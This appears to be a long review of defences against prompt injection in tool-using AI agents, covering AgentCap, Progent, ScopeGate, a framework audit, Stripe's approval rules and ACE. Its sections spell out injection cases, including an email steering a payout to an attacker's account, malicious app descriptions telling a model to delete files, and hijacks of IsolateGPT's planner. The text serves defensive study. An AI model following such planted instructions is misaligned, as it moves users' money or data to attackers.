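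The newest version lets a program send sealed data off the machine to a permitted host, for example to log in to a service with a key that the agent can't read. As documented, this is risky if the operator has not listed the permitted hosts. A hijacked agent could request access to the attacker's server by name and post the sealed key to it, using only operations that the compiler allows. Operators who keep secrets on the machine therefore need to set the host list themselves.

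## AgentCap: a signed token for each tool call

TACIT's types don't restrict which account an agent can pay. AgentCap, built by two researchers at Virginia Tech, addresses this problem without requiring the agent to write typed code. A gateway between the model and its tools checks every tool call, including its argument values. If the call passes, the gateway issues a capability as a signed token, and the tool runs only if the token is valid.

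Suresh and Gao (2026) argue in *AgentCap* that most agents merge two decisions that security systems keep separate: which action to take and whether that action is authorized. They let the model choose the action but not decide whether it is authorized.

### From a proposed payment to a signed token

Suppose a user asks a banking agent to send $50 to an account and types the account number in the request. The model proposes a call to `send_money` with a recipient and an amount. It must also declare an intent, chosen from a fixed list that AgentCap adds to the tool's description. A wrapper around the bank's MCP server intercepts the call and asks the gateway for authorization. The gateway consults a policy that the developer wrote beforehand. In AgentCap's policy language, a simplified rule for payments could look like this, with invented names for the action, resource, intent and prerequisite:

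```
grant send_money {
  action: send
  resource: money
  intent: pay_recipient
  requires: read_balance
  trust: >= 0.8
  bound_params: recipient
  ttl: 30s
  budget: 1
  tool: send_money
}
```

AgentCap runs seven checks before it issues a token. One requires the declared intent to be on the rule's list. This check is weak by itself, since a hijacked model can simply declare `pay_recipient`. Another requires the agent to have completed certain steps before it makes the call. An injected instruction to pay at once would fail this check, but an attacker who knew the policy could tell the agent to read the balance first.

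AgentCap also prevents an agent from holding two capabilities that a policy marks as dangerous together, such as reading customer records and writing to outsiders. If a developer lists three capabilities in one prohibition, the software bans every pair, so the developer can't use the prohibition to allow any two of them while forbidding all three together.

The trust check uses a score based on the agent's record. The score starts at 0.8 by default, and each anomaly, such as a denied request, cuts it by 30%. If the score doesn't recover between anomalies, it falls to 0.56, then 0.39, then 0.27. The third anomaly takes it below the default limit, and AgentCap isolates the agent.

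A payment needs a score of at least 0.8, so a single denial blocks payments until the score recovers. An attacker who can't steal money could still plant an instruction that provokes one forbidden call, after which the user's own payment would fail. Suresh and Gao report that none of the 23 trust settings they tried blocked a legitimate request. However, the settings included starting scores of 0.6 and 0.7, at which the payment rule would refuse every payment, so the request they tested must have had a lower threshold.

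If the call passes all the checks, AgentCap signs a token for the action and resource. The token expires after 30 seconds and can be used once. The gateway then verifies it at the tool's boundary and forwards the call to the bank. Issuing a token took a median of 66.9 microseconds and verifying one took 79.9, both negligible compared with a model's response time.

AgentCap checks the recipient and the amount when it issues the token, but the token doesn't contain them. The protection therefore depends on the software forwarding exactly the call that AgentCap checked. If the token were separated from that call, it would permit a payment to anyone. *Insuring Every Action* (2026) proposes a token that contains a hash of the exact action, a short fingerprint that no longer matches if someone changes the recipient. This proposed token also contains a hash of the data behind the decision and becomes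 unusable if that data has since changed.

As with TACIT, the agent must have no other route to its tools, and the check must happen outside the model. *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (2026) describes a related design that puts a signed token into the model's prompt and tells the model that risky calls require it. The paper treats this instruction as advice the model may ignore, so the design relies on separate software to verify the token before a tool runs.

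### Where the recipient came from

The line `bound_params: recipient` turns on the most important check against prompt injection, which accepts a recipient if trusted context supports it. AgentCap treats the user's request as trusted. The policy can label each tool's output, or individual fields of it, as trusted or tainted, and AgentCap carries these labels forward to later calls.

If the user typed the account number, the payment in the example goes through. If the agent reads an email with instructions to send the money to a different account, and the model tries to follow them, AgentCap does not issue a token, because the new number appears only in the body of the email, which the policy labels as tainted. AgentCap returns the reason to the agent, which can then continue the user's task.

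Bills are harder because a user who asks an agent to pay one usually hasn't typed the payee's account number, and the only copy may be in a file that somebody else sent. If the policy labels the file as tainted, AgentCap refuses a legitimate payment, but if the policy labels it as trusted, whoever wrote the file can choose the recipient. The second case is Rajani and colleagues' value attack, which a token doesn't prevent.

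Knowing where a value came from also doesn't show what the user meant it for. A user might mention two accounts, one to pay and one to close. An injection that caused the model to pay the second account would probably pass the provenance check, because the user supplied the number. The attacker would gain only if they controlled that account, so the check still removes most opportunities for theft.

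### Passing a token to another agent

An agent may hand part of its work to a second agent and give it a token derived from its own. AgentCap permits this only within one session, and the new token has to satisfy five conditions:

```
child.action    =  parent.action
child.resource  =  parent.resource
child.budget    ≤  parent.budget
child.lifetime  ≤  parent.lifetime
child.depth     <  parent.depth
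```

The budget is the number of uses, and the depth is how many more times agents can pass the authority on. The depth decreases with each delegation, so the chain must end. The policy also states which types of agent may delegate to which others. Processing a three-level chain took a median of 151.4 microseconds.

AgentCap's rule allows only limited attenuation, because the action and resource must stay the same. It has no equivalent of the read-only calendar. An agent with a token for payments can give its helper a token that allows fewer payments or expires sooner, but it can't use this rule to narrow a general right to pay into a right to pay only the electricity company.

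### Results on AgentDojo and InjecAgent

Suresh and Gao tested GPT-4o and GPT-5.4 on both benchmarks, with and without AgentCap, and used the same tasks and attacks in both conditions.

| Benchmark and model | Attack success without AgentCap | Attack success with AgentCap | Utility under attack without AgentCap | Utility under attack with AgentCap |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% | 5.09% | 73.61% | 74.88% |
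| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% | 0% | 75.68% | 75.04% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% | 8.63% | 74.10% | 62.24% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% | 0% | 72.96% | 65.37% |

These attacks often succeeded against the undefended agents, unlike the injection trials in TACIT's leak test, so there was something for the defence to prevent. The researchers ran each condition only once. The differences in attack rates are far too large to be chance, but the difference in GPT-5.4's utility on AgentDojo is about four cases, so a single run is weaker evidence there. They also ran GPT-5.4 with its reasoning turned off, so the undefended rates may not represent the model as people normally use it.

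Models complete fewer tasks with AgentCap even when nobody attacks. On AgentDojo's 97 user tasks, GPT-4o completed three fewer (3.1 percentage points) and GPT-5.4 seven fewer (7.2 points). On InjecAgent, the losses were 11.7 and 5.9 points, but they were measured on only 17 distinct tasks, so they amount to two tasks for GPT-4o and one for GPT-5.4. GPT-4o's drop of nearly 12 points on InjecAgent under attack is better evidence that the checks sometimes block useful work.

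The attacks that still succeeded against GPT-4o fall into three groups. In the first, the attacker only wanted the agent to write something in its answer, which a check on tool calls can't prevent. In the second, the attacker chose the value of an argument that the policy didn't list as sensitive. In the third, the value of a sensitive argument came through a field that the policy had left unlabeled. AgentCap evidently let such values through, so an attack can succeed if a developer forgets a label. Suresh and Gao call the last two groups policy gaps rather than enforcement failures. The distinction helps whoever repairs the system, but an attacker can exploit a policy gap just as well as a bug in the gateway.

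These gaps also limit what the zeros for GPT-5.4 show about AgentCap. Both models ran under the same policies, so the gaps that let attacks through with GPT-4o were still there, but the attacks that GPT-5.4 followed happened not to use them. Someone who knew the policy could write injections that did. The benchmark didn't test this, because its attacks weren't adapted to AgentCap.

Another developer also might not write policies as good as these. Suresh and Gao wrote them from the benchmark's tool definitions and its descriptions of the user tasks. They took the sensible precautions of freezing the policies before the test runs and including no rules that match the text of particular attacks, but they knew every task the agent would have to perform. A bank that deploys an agent doesn't know what all its customers will ask for, so its policy would probably block more legitimate requests or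 leave more openings for attacks. The InjecAgent policy had an even greater advantage, because Suresh and Gao built it partly from a list that gives the correct tool for each user task.

AgentCap includes a program that checks a policy for mistakes before anyone uses it. In a customer-service policy with eight capabilities, it examined all 28 pairs and found six that the policy prohibits. It also found that no agent could ever use `delete_customer`, because the steps required beforehand conflicted with a prohibition. The banking policy had a similar mistake, which the researchers corrected. Even the language's designers made errors in short policies, although these errors blocked legitimate actions and didn't let attackers in.

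The benchmarks can't show how much the tokens contributed. AgentCap combines them with checks on provenance, prerequisites and forbidden combinations, and Suresh and Gao compare the whole combination with no defence. The agents in these benchmarks work alone, so the delegation rule never applied. A gateway that ran the same seven checks and allowed or refused each call without issuing tokens would probably have blocked the same attacks.

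### Comparison with Progent

Progent, which Shi, He and colleagues (2025) describe as privilege control, is close to such a gateway but uses no tokens. Its rules specify which tools an agent may call and with which argument values, and it blocks any call that no rule allows. A language model writes the rules for each task from the user's request, before it sees any outside content, and can propose changes as tool results come in.

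In one example, a user asks an agent to carry out a to-do list that Alice has emailed. At first, the rules allow only a search for Alice's email. The list asks the agent to post a summary of recent emails to the user's Slack account, so the model proposes to allow reading emails and posting to Slack. After the agent looks up the user's Slack name, the model narrows the posting rule to that name. One of the emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. Progent blocks the forwarding call if the rules still don't mention `send_email`.

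An injection might also mislead the model that writes the rules. Progent therefore compares each proposed set of rules with the current one, using an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all be true. If *A(P)* is the set of tool calls that the rules *P* allow, then new rules *P′* take effect automatically only when

*A(P′) ⊆ A(P)*.

Progent treats every other change as an expansion, which needs approval. Without approval, the set of permitted calls can only stay the same or shrink. Progent also compares argument values, which AgentCap's delegation rule does not, so it can classify permission to message one person as narrower than permission to message anyone.

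With GPT-4o, Shi and colleagues reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. On ASB, another benchmark for agents, it fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. They approved every expansion automatically in these tests, to imitate a careless user. The solver could label a change as an expansion but couldn't block it, so its guarantee didn't affect the main results. Most of the protection came from the first set of rules, which alone reduced the rate on AgentDojo to 2.5%. When a person reviewed the first rules and every expansion, the rate fell to 0%. Only 6% of changes were expansions, so the solver's main benefit may be that people don't have to review the other 94%.

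*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticizes Progent because hand-written rules are prone to error and because hostile tool results may lead the model to loosen its limits. Shi and colleagues tested the second possibility. One of their adapted attacks told the model that writes the rules to permit the tools the attacker needed, and another used a program to search for injections that work. With automatic approval still on, these attacks raised the attack success rate only slightly. AgentCap hasn't been tested against comparable attacks on either benchmark.

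Suresh and Gao ran Progent themselves on AgentDojo and report that AgentCap had a lower attack success rate and higher utility. With GPT-4o and no attack, the agent completed 76 of the 97 user tasks (78.35%) with AgentCap and 66 (68.04%) with Progent. They explain that Progent's model often limits an argument to the values it predicts from the request, so Progent blocks legitimate calls with other values. AgentCap accepts any value that trusted context supports. This explanation is plausible, but the people who wrote AgentCap's policies could also see all the tasks, while Progent's model wrote its rules from one request at a time.

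The comparison under attack is less reliable. Suresh and Gao state that both systems faced the same 949 cases, but their percentages for AgentCap don't correspond to whole numbers of cases out of 949. Its attack success rate of 5.09%, for example, would be 48.3 cases. All of the AgentDojo figures in the table above match whole numbers out of the 629 cases in the first release by Debenedetti and colleagues, where 5.09% is 32 cases. Progent's utility under attack, 59.64%, matches 566 of 949 cases but no whole number out of 629. The two systems therefore seem to have run on different versions of the benchmark, in which case the published figures don't establish which one stops more attacks.

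Two of the attacker's goals in the Travel suite are to steer the agent toward a different, legitimate hotel. Shi and colleagues leave these out of their own tests because they don't claim that Progent prevents such attacks, but Suresh and Gao include them. Each goal is paired with 20 user tasks, so the two add 40 cases, which could raise Progent's attack success rate by as much as 4.2 percentage points.

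### The controlled scenarios

Five smaller tests examine AgentCap's mechanisms separately. In the first, a task needed four of eight available capabilities, and AgentCap issued only those four. In the second, which involved prompt injection, AgentCap completed the user's work and blocked all three malicious calls, while an agent with ambient authority carried out all three. Suresh and Gao also tried tokens limited only by time and budget, which allowed eight calls before the budget ran out. This comparison is the closest they come to separating the effect of the tokens from that of the policy. It supports the view that short-lived tokens alone give little protection against injection, and that AgentCap's protection comes from the checks it makes before issuing them.

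The fourth scenario tested two forbidden combinations of capabilities, and AgentCap blocked both. The third and fifth scenarios tested delegation and confused deputies. Across both, AgentCap rejected all nine attempts to enlarge a delegated token or use it in an unrelated session.

Nine attempts are very few for a claim about confused deputies. They resemble software tests, which confirm that the program follows its own rule in cases the programmers chose. Suresh and Gao also wrote 593 automated tests of the software's functions, which help find bugs but don't measure resistance to an attacker. *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* reports a test of a similar property in another design, where the software rejected all 452 attempts to reuse a single-use token. Every attempt came immediately after the first use and in the same process, which is the easiest case to get right.

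The nine attempts also differ from the attack on Hardy's compiler. Carrying a token into another session means using a stolen or misplaced credential, whereas Hardy's compiler used its own permission. A corresponding test for AgentCap would inject a recipient into a payment that the agent is entitled to make. The benchmarks contain attacks of that kind, so the 32 that succeeded on AgentDojo and the 91 on InjecAgent with GPT-4o are more informative about confused deputies than the nine rejections, although some of the 32 only affected the agent's text.

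### Object capability or policy check

AgentCap's tokens are capabilities because they are unforgeable and grant a stated right. Whether they are object capabilities depends on more than the signature. In *Comparing capability systems* (Karp, 2026), a mailing-list discussion about delegation to AI agents, Mark Miller separates the access-control model from the technology that implements it. He counts operating systems, programming languages and signed certificates among the technologies that can support capabilities. By this reasoning, AgentCap shouldn't be ruled out as an object-capability system merely because it uses a signed token where TACIT uses a reference in a program.

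Using a policy to decide who receives a token doesn't rule AgentCap out as a capability system either. In any such system, someone has to hand out the first capabilities, usually by some rule. Miller and colleagues discuss a design in which an oracle grants capabilities on request, depending on the requester's security clearance and the file's secrecy. They show that this design can keep secrets from leaking if the system separates the right to pass data from the right to pass capabilities, and they still regard it as a pure capability system. AgentCap's gateway has a similar role to the oracle. *From ABAC to ZBAC* (Karp, Haury and Davis, 2009) likewise lets an organization use its own policy to decide which authorizations its members get. The essential requirement in its model is that the member presents the authorization with the request, so the service only has to verify it.

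But they make the policy decision before the request, while AgentCap makes it afterwards. The gateway decides whether to issue a token only after the model proposes a payment. The agent has no right to pay before the token is issued or after it expires 30 seconds later. In between, the token lets the gateway confirm the decision it has just made. Between calls, the agent's authority consists of the developer's policy, which AgentCap consults each time, much as the operating system consulted the compiler's licence.

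In AgentCap, the model names a tool and an account in plain text and doesn't have to choose a capability. Miller and colleagues compare two people who each have a ring of keys. One picks a key for a purpose and then goes to the door, while the other goes to a door and tries every key. The second person can become a confused deputy even though the keys are unforgeable. An AgentCap agent is like the second person, because it proposes an action and the gateway looks for a rule that fits. An injected account number needs no reference to go with it, so AgentCap depends on the provenance check to reject it. If the policy lacks a label, nothing else about the token prevents the payment.

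The rights are also coarse. The paper maps each tool in a benchmark to one action and one resource, so the banking policy has 11 capabilities regardless of how many accounts exist. POSIX's fixed flags have the same limitation.

For an agent's own calls, then, AgentCap is best understood as a policy check expressed as a token. Delegation is a better case for calling it a capability system. An agent that holds a right can give it to a second agent that lacked it, and the second agent can pass on no more than it received. Restricting tokens to one session also gives AgentCap some of the control over delegation that ordinary signed certificates lack. But delegation has the least evidence behind it, because only some of the nine attempts and the software tests exercised it.

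*Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents* (2026) proposes tokens that the user signs for a particular agent, with limits on what that agent may do. The agent can derive tokens for other agents from its own. A service would check the agent's identity, the user's identity and the limits. If the user signed a token for one payment to one account before the agent opened any email, the token would not cover a payment to an injected account number. But the user would have to know the account number in advance, so this would help little with the bill whose payee appears only in the file.

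## ScopeGate and an audit of three agent frameworks

Developers have to install AgentCap or Progent separately, and many start with only a framework, a library that connects a model to its tools. Mellafe Zuvic's 2026 audit examined the default behavior of three frameworks: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to the payment company Stripe. All three limit which tools a model can call, but none checks whether a particular call should run given its argument values.

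### What the frameworks check by default

Mellafe Zuvic read each framework's public source code at a fixed version, so anyone can check the findings against the same code. In capability gating, a developer gives the agent a list of tools, and the model can't call anything else. Each tool also has a schema that describes its arguments and can require an account identifier to be text and an amount to be a number. A stranger's account identifier is also text, so it fits the schema too.

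In Stripe's toolkit, the permissions on the developer's API key determine which tools the agent gets, according to a copy of the toolkit's documentation on Glama. Stripe's *Restricted API keys* explains that an ordinary secret key lets its holder do anything in the account, while a restricted key carries only the permissions the developer selects. No injection can make the agent issue a refund if its key doesn't permit refunds. But a key that permits them allows refunds requested in a stranger's email as well as deserved ones.

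The audit found that none of the three frameworks had, by default, a per-call authorization check that was both deterministic and fail-closed. A deterministic check always gives the same answer for the same call and policy, which rules out having a model decide. A fail-closed check refuses any call that no rule covers or that it can't interpret.

Dantuluri and Sundi (2026), in *Delegation Without Trust*, reached the same conclusion about LangGraph by running it. They replaced the model with a script, so that the result wouldn't depend on whether a model followed an injected instruction, and the tool calls outside the agent's task went through. They also inspected the code of CrewAI and AutoGen, two frameworks for teams of agents, and found no built-in authorization in either. Only LangChain and LangGraph appear in both studies, and Dantuluri and Sundi work for VotalAI, which sells a product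 meant to fill this gap. But the source code is public, so the finding doesn't depend much on trusting either study.

People could disagree about whether the missing check is a flaw in the frameworks. Mellafe Zuvic reports no specific vulnerability and treats the findings as candidates for hardening. Dantuluri and Sundi acknowledge that none of the frameworks they studied claims to be an authorization system. A framework's maintainers also can't know which accounts a company has verified, so they can't supply the right rules. But they could make the framework refuse to run a tool that moves money until the developer supplies a policy, whereas the audited frameworks run it without one. A developer who connects a payment tool to an agent that reads email therefore has to add the check, or the agent could become a confused deputy.

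### A payout to the wrong account

Suppose a company uses an agent to pay a merchant whose verified account is `acct_MERCHANT_001`. The agent holds the company's payment key and reads its email. An attacker sends a message, written like a routine notice from a finance department, with new account details for the merchant. The model accepts the change and proposes this call (the tool's name and the amount are invented here):

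```
send_payout(account="acct_ATTACKER_999", amount=500)
```

LangChain's default dispatch finds the tool and runs the call. Mellafe Zuvic demonstrated this with the framework's real code and a mocked payment service, so no money moved. A companion demonstration shows the same for LlamaIndex. ScopeGate, Mellafe Zuvic's gate for tool calls, rejects the identical call because the account isn't in the verified set.

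The attacker has no right to spend the company's money, but the agent does. The framework runs the call with the company's key without checking who supplied the account identifier, much as the operating system in Hardy's example didn't check who had supplied the name of the billing file. Gating can't prevent this, because paying the merchant requires the same tool as paying the attacker.

The demonstration feeds a fixed call to the framework and then to the gate. This is the right way to test whether they check calls, but it doesn't show how often a real model would propose such a call, which Mellafe Zuvic measured separately.

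### ScopeGate's five checks

ScopeGate sits between the model and the tools, and a call runs only if it passes every stage:

1. **Scope.** The agent must have permission to use this tool at all.
2. **Authorization.** Sensitive argument values must be on an allowlist. In the example, the list of payees contains only `acct_MERCHANT_001`.
3. **Money ceiling.** The amount must not exceed a limit.
4. **Idempotency.** A payment must carry a key that identifies it, so that a repeated request doesn't pay twice.
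5. **Default denial.** If no rule allows the call, ScopeGate refuses it.

Only the second check, the allowlist, protects against a substituted account. The attacker's payout could pass the others because the agent has permission to make payouts, 500 may be a normal amount, and the software can attach a valid key to a fraudulent payment as easily as to a real one.

The list of payees and the ceiling have to come from a source that the model can't change. If the model could add payees, an attacker would only need to write an email asking it to register a new account and then pay that account. ScopeGate's policy comes entirely from the operator, whereas Progent lets a model write some of its policy.

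An attacker can still get text into ScopeGate's policy by deceiving the people who maintain it. In ordinary business email fraud, a criminal poses as a supplier and asks the accounts department to update the supplier's bank details. If an employee believes the same email that misled the model and adds the new account to ScopeGate's list, the gate will approve the payment. To prevent this, a company would need to confirm the change through another channel, such as a phone number it already has on file.

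ScopeGate also handles unfamiliar payees more crudely than AgentCap, because it doesn't track where values came from. A payment to a new account fails until the operator lists the account, even if the user typed it in the request. But the operator doesn't have to label tool outputs, so a forgotten label can't let a payment through. This design suits a company that pays the same merchants every week better than a person who pays a different bill each time.

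### The same tool as an object capability

ScopeGate leaves the payment tool able to pay anyone and then restricts what the model may ask of it. An object-capability design would instead give the agent a tool that can pay only one merchant. In Python, the software around the agent could create it like this:

```python
def make_payout_tool(merchant_account, limit):
    remaining = limit

    def pay_merchant(amount):
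        nonlocal remaining
        if not 0 < amount <= remaining:
            raise PermissionError("outside the payout limit")
        remaining -= amount
        merchant_account.pay(amount)

    return pay_merchant
```

Before the agent reads any email, the software looks up the merchant in the company's records and calls `make_payout_tool` with a reference to that merchant's account. It then gives the agent only the inner function, `pay_merchant`. The account reference is built into this function, a way of passing on access that Miller and colleagues call endowment. The model supplies only one argument, the amount.

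An attacker can still persuade the model that the merchant has moved to `acct_ATTACKER_999`, but the function has no parameter for an account. If the model adds an `account` argument anyway, the call is malformed. This protection doesn't depend on an allowlist catching the substitution or on someone remembering to write a rule for the account argument. The function also attenuates the right to pay, because the sum of all its payments can't exceed `limit`. With only a per-call limit, a series of small payments could add up to more than that.

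Several attacks remain:

- An injection can trigger a payment that nobody requested, or change the amount within the limit. The money goes to the real merchant, so this mostly benefits an attacker who is the merchant, or works with them.
- The attacker may have changed the company's records before the software looked up the account. The reference then points faithfully to the wrong place.
- If the agent holds references to several merchants, an injection can influence which one it pays.
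- Other tools are unaffected. An agent that can also send email can still leak the payment history.

With one merchant, the reference and ScopeGate's one-item allowlist stop the same substitution. They differ when there is more than one. Suppose the operator lists merchants A and B, and today's task is to pay A. An injection that substitutes B's account passes the allowlist, whereas an agent that received only the reference to A can't make that payment. ScopeGate could also block the payment if the operator gave it a new list for each task, but someone would have to write each list, just as someone has to choose the references.

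The redesign assumes that the agent can act only through tool calls, in which case the boundary between the model and the surrounding software is enough to keep it from bypassing the limit. An agent that could run its own Python in the same process might extract `merchant_account` and call it without the limit, because Python lets code inspect the values stored inside a function. TACIT's safe mode bans this kind of inspection in Scala.

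Stripe already offers part of this design. Some of its customers are platforms that handle payments for many businesses, each with its own connected account. Stripe's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, the documentation for its tool server, describes a `Stripe-Account` header that specifies the connected account for a call. The developer sets the header in the agent's configuration, so the model doesn't have to name the account. The toolkit on Glama has a similar `account` setting, but it is only a default, so a developer should make sure that nothing in a tool call can override it.

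Both settings fix the account the agent works for, so they would keep a support agent for one shop out of another shop's records. They don't fix who receives a payment, so they would not by themselves have stopped the payout to the attacker. Neither is a strict object capability, in which a reference to one account would carry no authority over the others. The header is an ordinary identifier, and the key sent with it belongs to the platform and carries whatever permissions over connected accounts the platform has given it. Anyone who obtained the key could pair it with a different account identifier.

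### The tests

Mellafe Zuvic tested ScopeGate with prepared tool calls, with a model that tried to bypass it, and with models that had read a prompt injection.

| Test | Trials | Unauthorized calls proposed | Unauthorized calls allowed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed cases | 48 | 48 | 0 |
| Adaptive attacker (GLM-5.2) | 40 | 29 | 0 |
| Latam-GPT after an injection | 10 | 10 | 0 |
| GLM-4.5-Air after an injection | 10 | 10 | 0 |
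| GPT-4o mini after an injection | 10 | 10 | 0 |

The 48 fixed cases cover tool names, argument types, amounts and missing idempotency keys. They mainly test how the program handles unusual input, which matters because an allowlist gives no protection if a badly formed call gets past the comparison. One published check, for example, confirms that ScopeGate refuses an amount that isn't a valid number. The tests are easy to reproduce because the code is open source and a single command runs the demonstration and the fixed cases.

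In the adaptive test, the language model GLM-5.2 had 40 attempts to produce a harmful call that ScopeGate would allow. Nine outputs were malformed, and two were legitimate calls, which the gate allowed. That leaves 29 real attempts, which is few for an attacker. Mellafe Zuvic states that neither this result nor the fixed cases prove that a bypass is impossible.

A more basic limitation is that both tests define an unauthorized call as one that breaks the policy, so they can find errors in the gate but not in the policy. If an injection caused the agent to pay a listed merchant for work nobody had done, the payment would count as authorized. Rajani and colleagues' value attacks take this form, and an attacker who had studied the allowlist would have good reason to try them.

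The tests with injected models show that the threat is realistic. After reading a subtle message about updated finance details, GLM-4.5-Air and GPT-4o mini both proposed the unauthorized payout in all ten trials. Latam-GPT, a Latin American model based on Llama 3.1, did the same in a Spanish-language scenario. It ran in compressed form and wrote its tool calls as plain text because its server didn't support the usual format, so its result may not reflect its behavior in a normal deployment.

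Mellafe Zuvic uses "attack success rate" for the share of trials in which the model proposes an unauthorized action, whether or not it is carried out. These rates aren't directly comparable with AgentDojo's, which count completed attacks. A model can score 100% here even if ScopeGate refused every call and no money was lost. One author wrote all the scenarios, and they all deliver the injection the same way and last a single turn.

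The evidence for ScopeGate is weakest on whether it lets legitimate work through. It refused none of ten benign calls, five from each of two models, and in a separate check it allowed all four authorized actions. A gate that wrongly refused one legitimate call in ten would still pass a test of ten independent calls about a third of the time. The result also depends on whether the test's authorized payees were already on the list. A company would want to know how often employees need to pay someone who isn't on the list, and how long they wait for the operator to add that payee. ScopeGate has no results on AgentDojo or InjecAgent, so there is no measure of how many complete tasks it would cause an agent to fail.

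One independent researcher conducted the audit, built the defence, wrote the attacks and simulated the payments. Readers can run the central demonstration themselves, so they have to take little on trust. The zeros in the table support a narrower claim, that ScopeGate correctly applied a simple policy to the calls it received.

### When one agent acts for another

ScopeGate checks a single agent's calls. If that agent passes work to a second one, a gate at the tool also needs information about the authority the second agent received. Dantuluri and Sundi point out that a policy engine can evaluate a call correctly and still authorize the wrong party if the credential behind the call is stolen or too broad.

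Their remedy is a broker that issues a signed token at each delegation. The new token can only narrow the old one's rights, expires quickly, and works only for the program it names. Before each tool call, the broker verifies the signature, the holder's identity and the limits, and checks whether anyone has revoked the token. Unlike AgentCap's delegation rule, the token's limits can reduce the set of tools and resources, so an agent with broad rights can pass on the right to a single action.

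The broker withstood 11 attacks on its design and rejected all 200,000 forged tokens. The forged-token result mostly confirms that random and altered tokens fail a standard signature check. In 2,000 simulated delegations, a hijacked helper could reach an average of 1.5 actions out of 8,100, compared with all 8,100 when it inherited a general credential. The average of 1.5 is the size of the tasks the simulation delegated, so it shows that the broker enforces its limits but doesn't show that developers could set limits this tight for real work.

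Dantuluri and Sundi also report that the broker blocks confused-deputy attacks. Checking tools and resources can stop these attacks only when the attacker wants something outside the delegated task. If the task includes payments to any account, the token also permits a payment to the attacker. The tests didn't use a live model, and the code isn't public.

### Changes to the defaults

None of the maintainers appears to have replied publicly to the audit. Dantuluri and Sundi wrote in August 2026 that they still planned to notify the maintainers of the frameworks in their own study.

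LangChain still runs tool calls without review by default, according to its current documentation. Its optional *HumanInTheLoopMiddleware* pauses an agent so a person can approve, edit or reject a tool call. The developer lists the tools that need review, and any unlisted tool is described there as "auto-approved by default". This fails open, because a dangerous tool that the developer forgets to list runs without review.

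The component can be configured to check argument values. LangChain's *Human in the loop* describes an optional function, `when`, that receives the proposed call and determines whether to pause. A developer could use it to send every payout to an unlisted account to a reviewer. The function runs again after the reviewer answers, and if it returns a different result, the tool can run even though the reviewer rejected the call. The function therefore shouldn't depend on anything that might change between runs, such as the time of day or a payee list that someone is editing.

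LangChain plans to make a "per-call" mode the default in its next major release. This mode pauses separately for each reviewed call, whereas the current default groups all the calls from one model response. The developer still chooses which tools need review, so the mode is not per-call authorization, despite its name. LangChain also provides a wrapper that runs around each tool call, where a developer can write an automatic refusal and could add ScopeGate's checks.

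Stripe's defaults are stricter, at least on its own server. According to the server's documentation, an agent connected through a user's login needs human confirmation for refunds, currency conversions and transfers of money. The user opens a link, reviews the details in Stripe's dashboard and approves the request, and the agent then retries it. Setting up a new recipient isn't marked as needing confirmation, so an injection might get an attacker's account registered without it. The user would still have to approve any payment to that account, but would need to notice the wrong recipient to stop it.

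Stripe's *Set up two-party approvals* lists default rules for agents that connect with a key. They cover refunds, cancelled subscriptions, outbound payments and transfers, payouts and currency conversions. The account's owner can edit or delete these rules, which apply to keys tagged "agent". From December 2026, Stripe's tool server will accept only keys with this tag.

These rules apply a check outside the model without any work by the developer, which is much of what the audit found missing. But a person has to judge the payment, whereas ScopeGate compares it with a list, so the rules depend on the reviewer's attention. They are also part of Stripe's service, and Mellafe Zuvic examined the toolkit's public code, not the inside of the remote server. Stripe doesn't date the rules or connect them with the audit, so they may predate it.

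Stripe's server also shows why a list of tool names is becoming a poor basis for review. In *Guardrails for money movement*, an older post on Stripe's developer blog, an agent reads a customer's email, compares it with a refund policy and pauses for approval before calling `create_refund`. The developer attached the pause to that tool's name. The current server handles refunds through a general tool, `stripe_api_write`, which also updates customers, creates invoices and performs many other actions. A pause attached to the old name would never trigger, and one attached to the new name would also interrupt harmless work. Stripe therefore bases its confirmations on the action each call requests, and developers who write their own checks must do the same.

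## ACE: separating apps and fixing the plan in advance

AgentCap and ScopeGate protect users from malicious text that reaches an agent through trustworthy tools. If an assistant lets people install apps from many developers, a tool may itself be malicious. *ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, 2026) presents an architecture for such assistants, named after its three stages: Abstract, Concrete and Execute. A model first plans how to carry out the user's request without seeing any installed app. The system then finds apps for the steps and runs each app in its own container, an isolated environment with limited access to the computer.

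An app has a function that does the work, a schema that lists its inputs and outputs, and a description in plain English. In most assistants, the model reads every installed app's description before it chooses what to do, so an app can interfere with unrelated requests. In a conference talk on the system, Mallick, Rose and colleagues (2026) give the example of a user who asks to email a file. The description of an installed maths app is an instruction to call the disk app and delete all files, and the model may follow it.

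### Attacks from an installed app

An earlier defence, IsolateGPT, ran each app in isolation. But one central model still read the apps' descriptions to choose among them, and another read each app's output to decide the next step. Li and colleagues attacked IsolateGPT's public code through both the descriptions and the outputs. In their example, a user wants the fare from Main Street to Elms Avenue and has two apps that calculate fares, the legitimate MetroHail and the malicious QuickRide.

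- **Planner manipulation.** QuickRide's description tells the model to use QuickRide and not MetroHail. IsolateGPT left MetroHail out of its plan, and the user saw only QuickRide's fare.
- **Execution flow disruption.** Instead of a fare, QuickRide returns a warning that criminals are using all fare calculators to distribute drugs. IsolateGPT stopped before it ran MetroHail and told the user there was a technical error.
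- **Execution manager hijack.** MetroHail returns $54. QuickRide then returns an instruction to report $54 as its own fare and $85 as MetroHail's, and IsolateGPT did so.

QuickRide never had to break out of its isolation, because the text it supplied reached a model that controlled the rest of the request.

### The abstract plan

ACE's planning model receives the user's request and, optionally, a description of the setting from a trusted source. It first invents the apps it would like to have. These abstract apps have names, descriptions and types for their inputs and outputs, but no code. In a second call, the model writes a program that uses them. For the two fares, a simplified plan could look like this:

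```python
def main():
    metro: float = MetroHailFare(start="Main Street", end="Elms Avenue")
    quick: float = QuickRideFare(start="Main Street", end="Elms Avenue")
    display(f"MetroHail: {metro}, QuickRide: {quick}")
    return "done"
```

The planning model would write the same program whether or not the user had installed QuickRide, so QuickRide's description can't affect the program. No model can add a step once execution starts.

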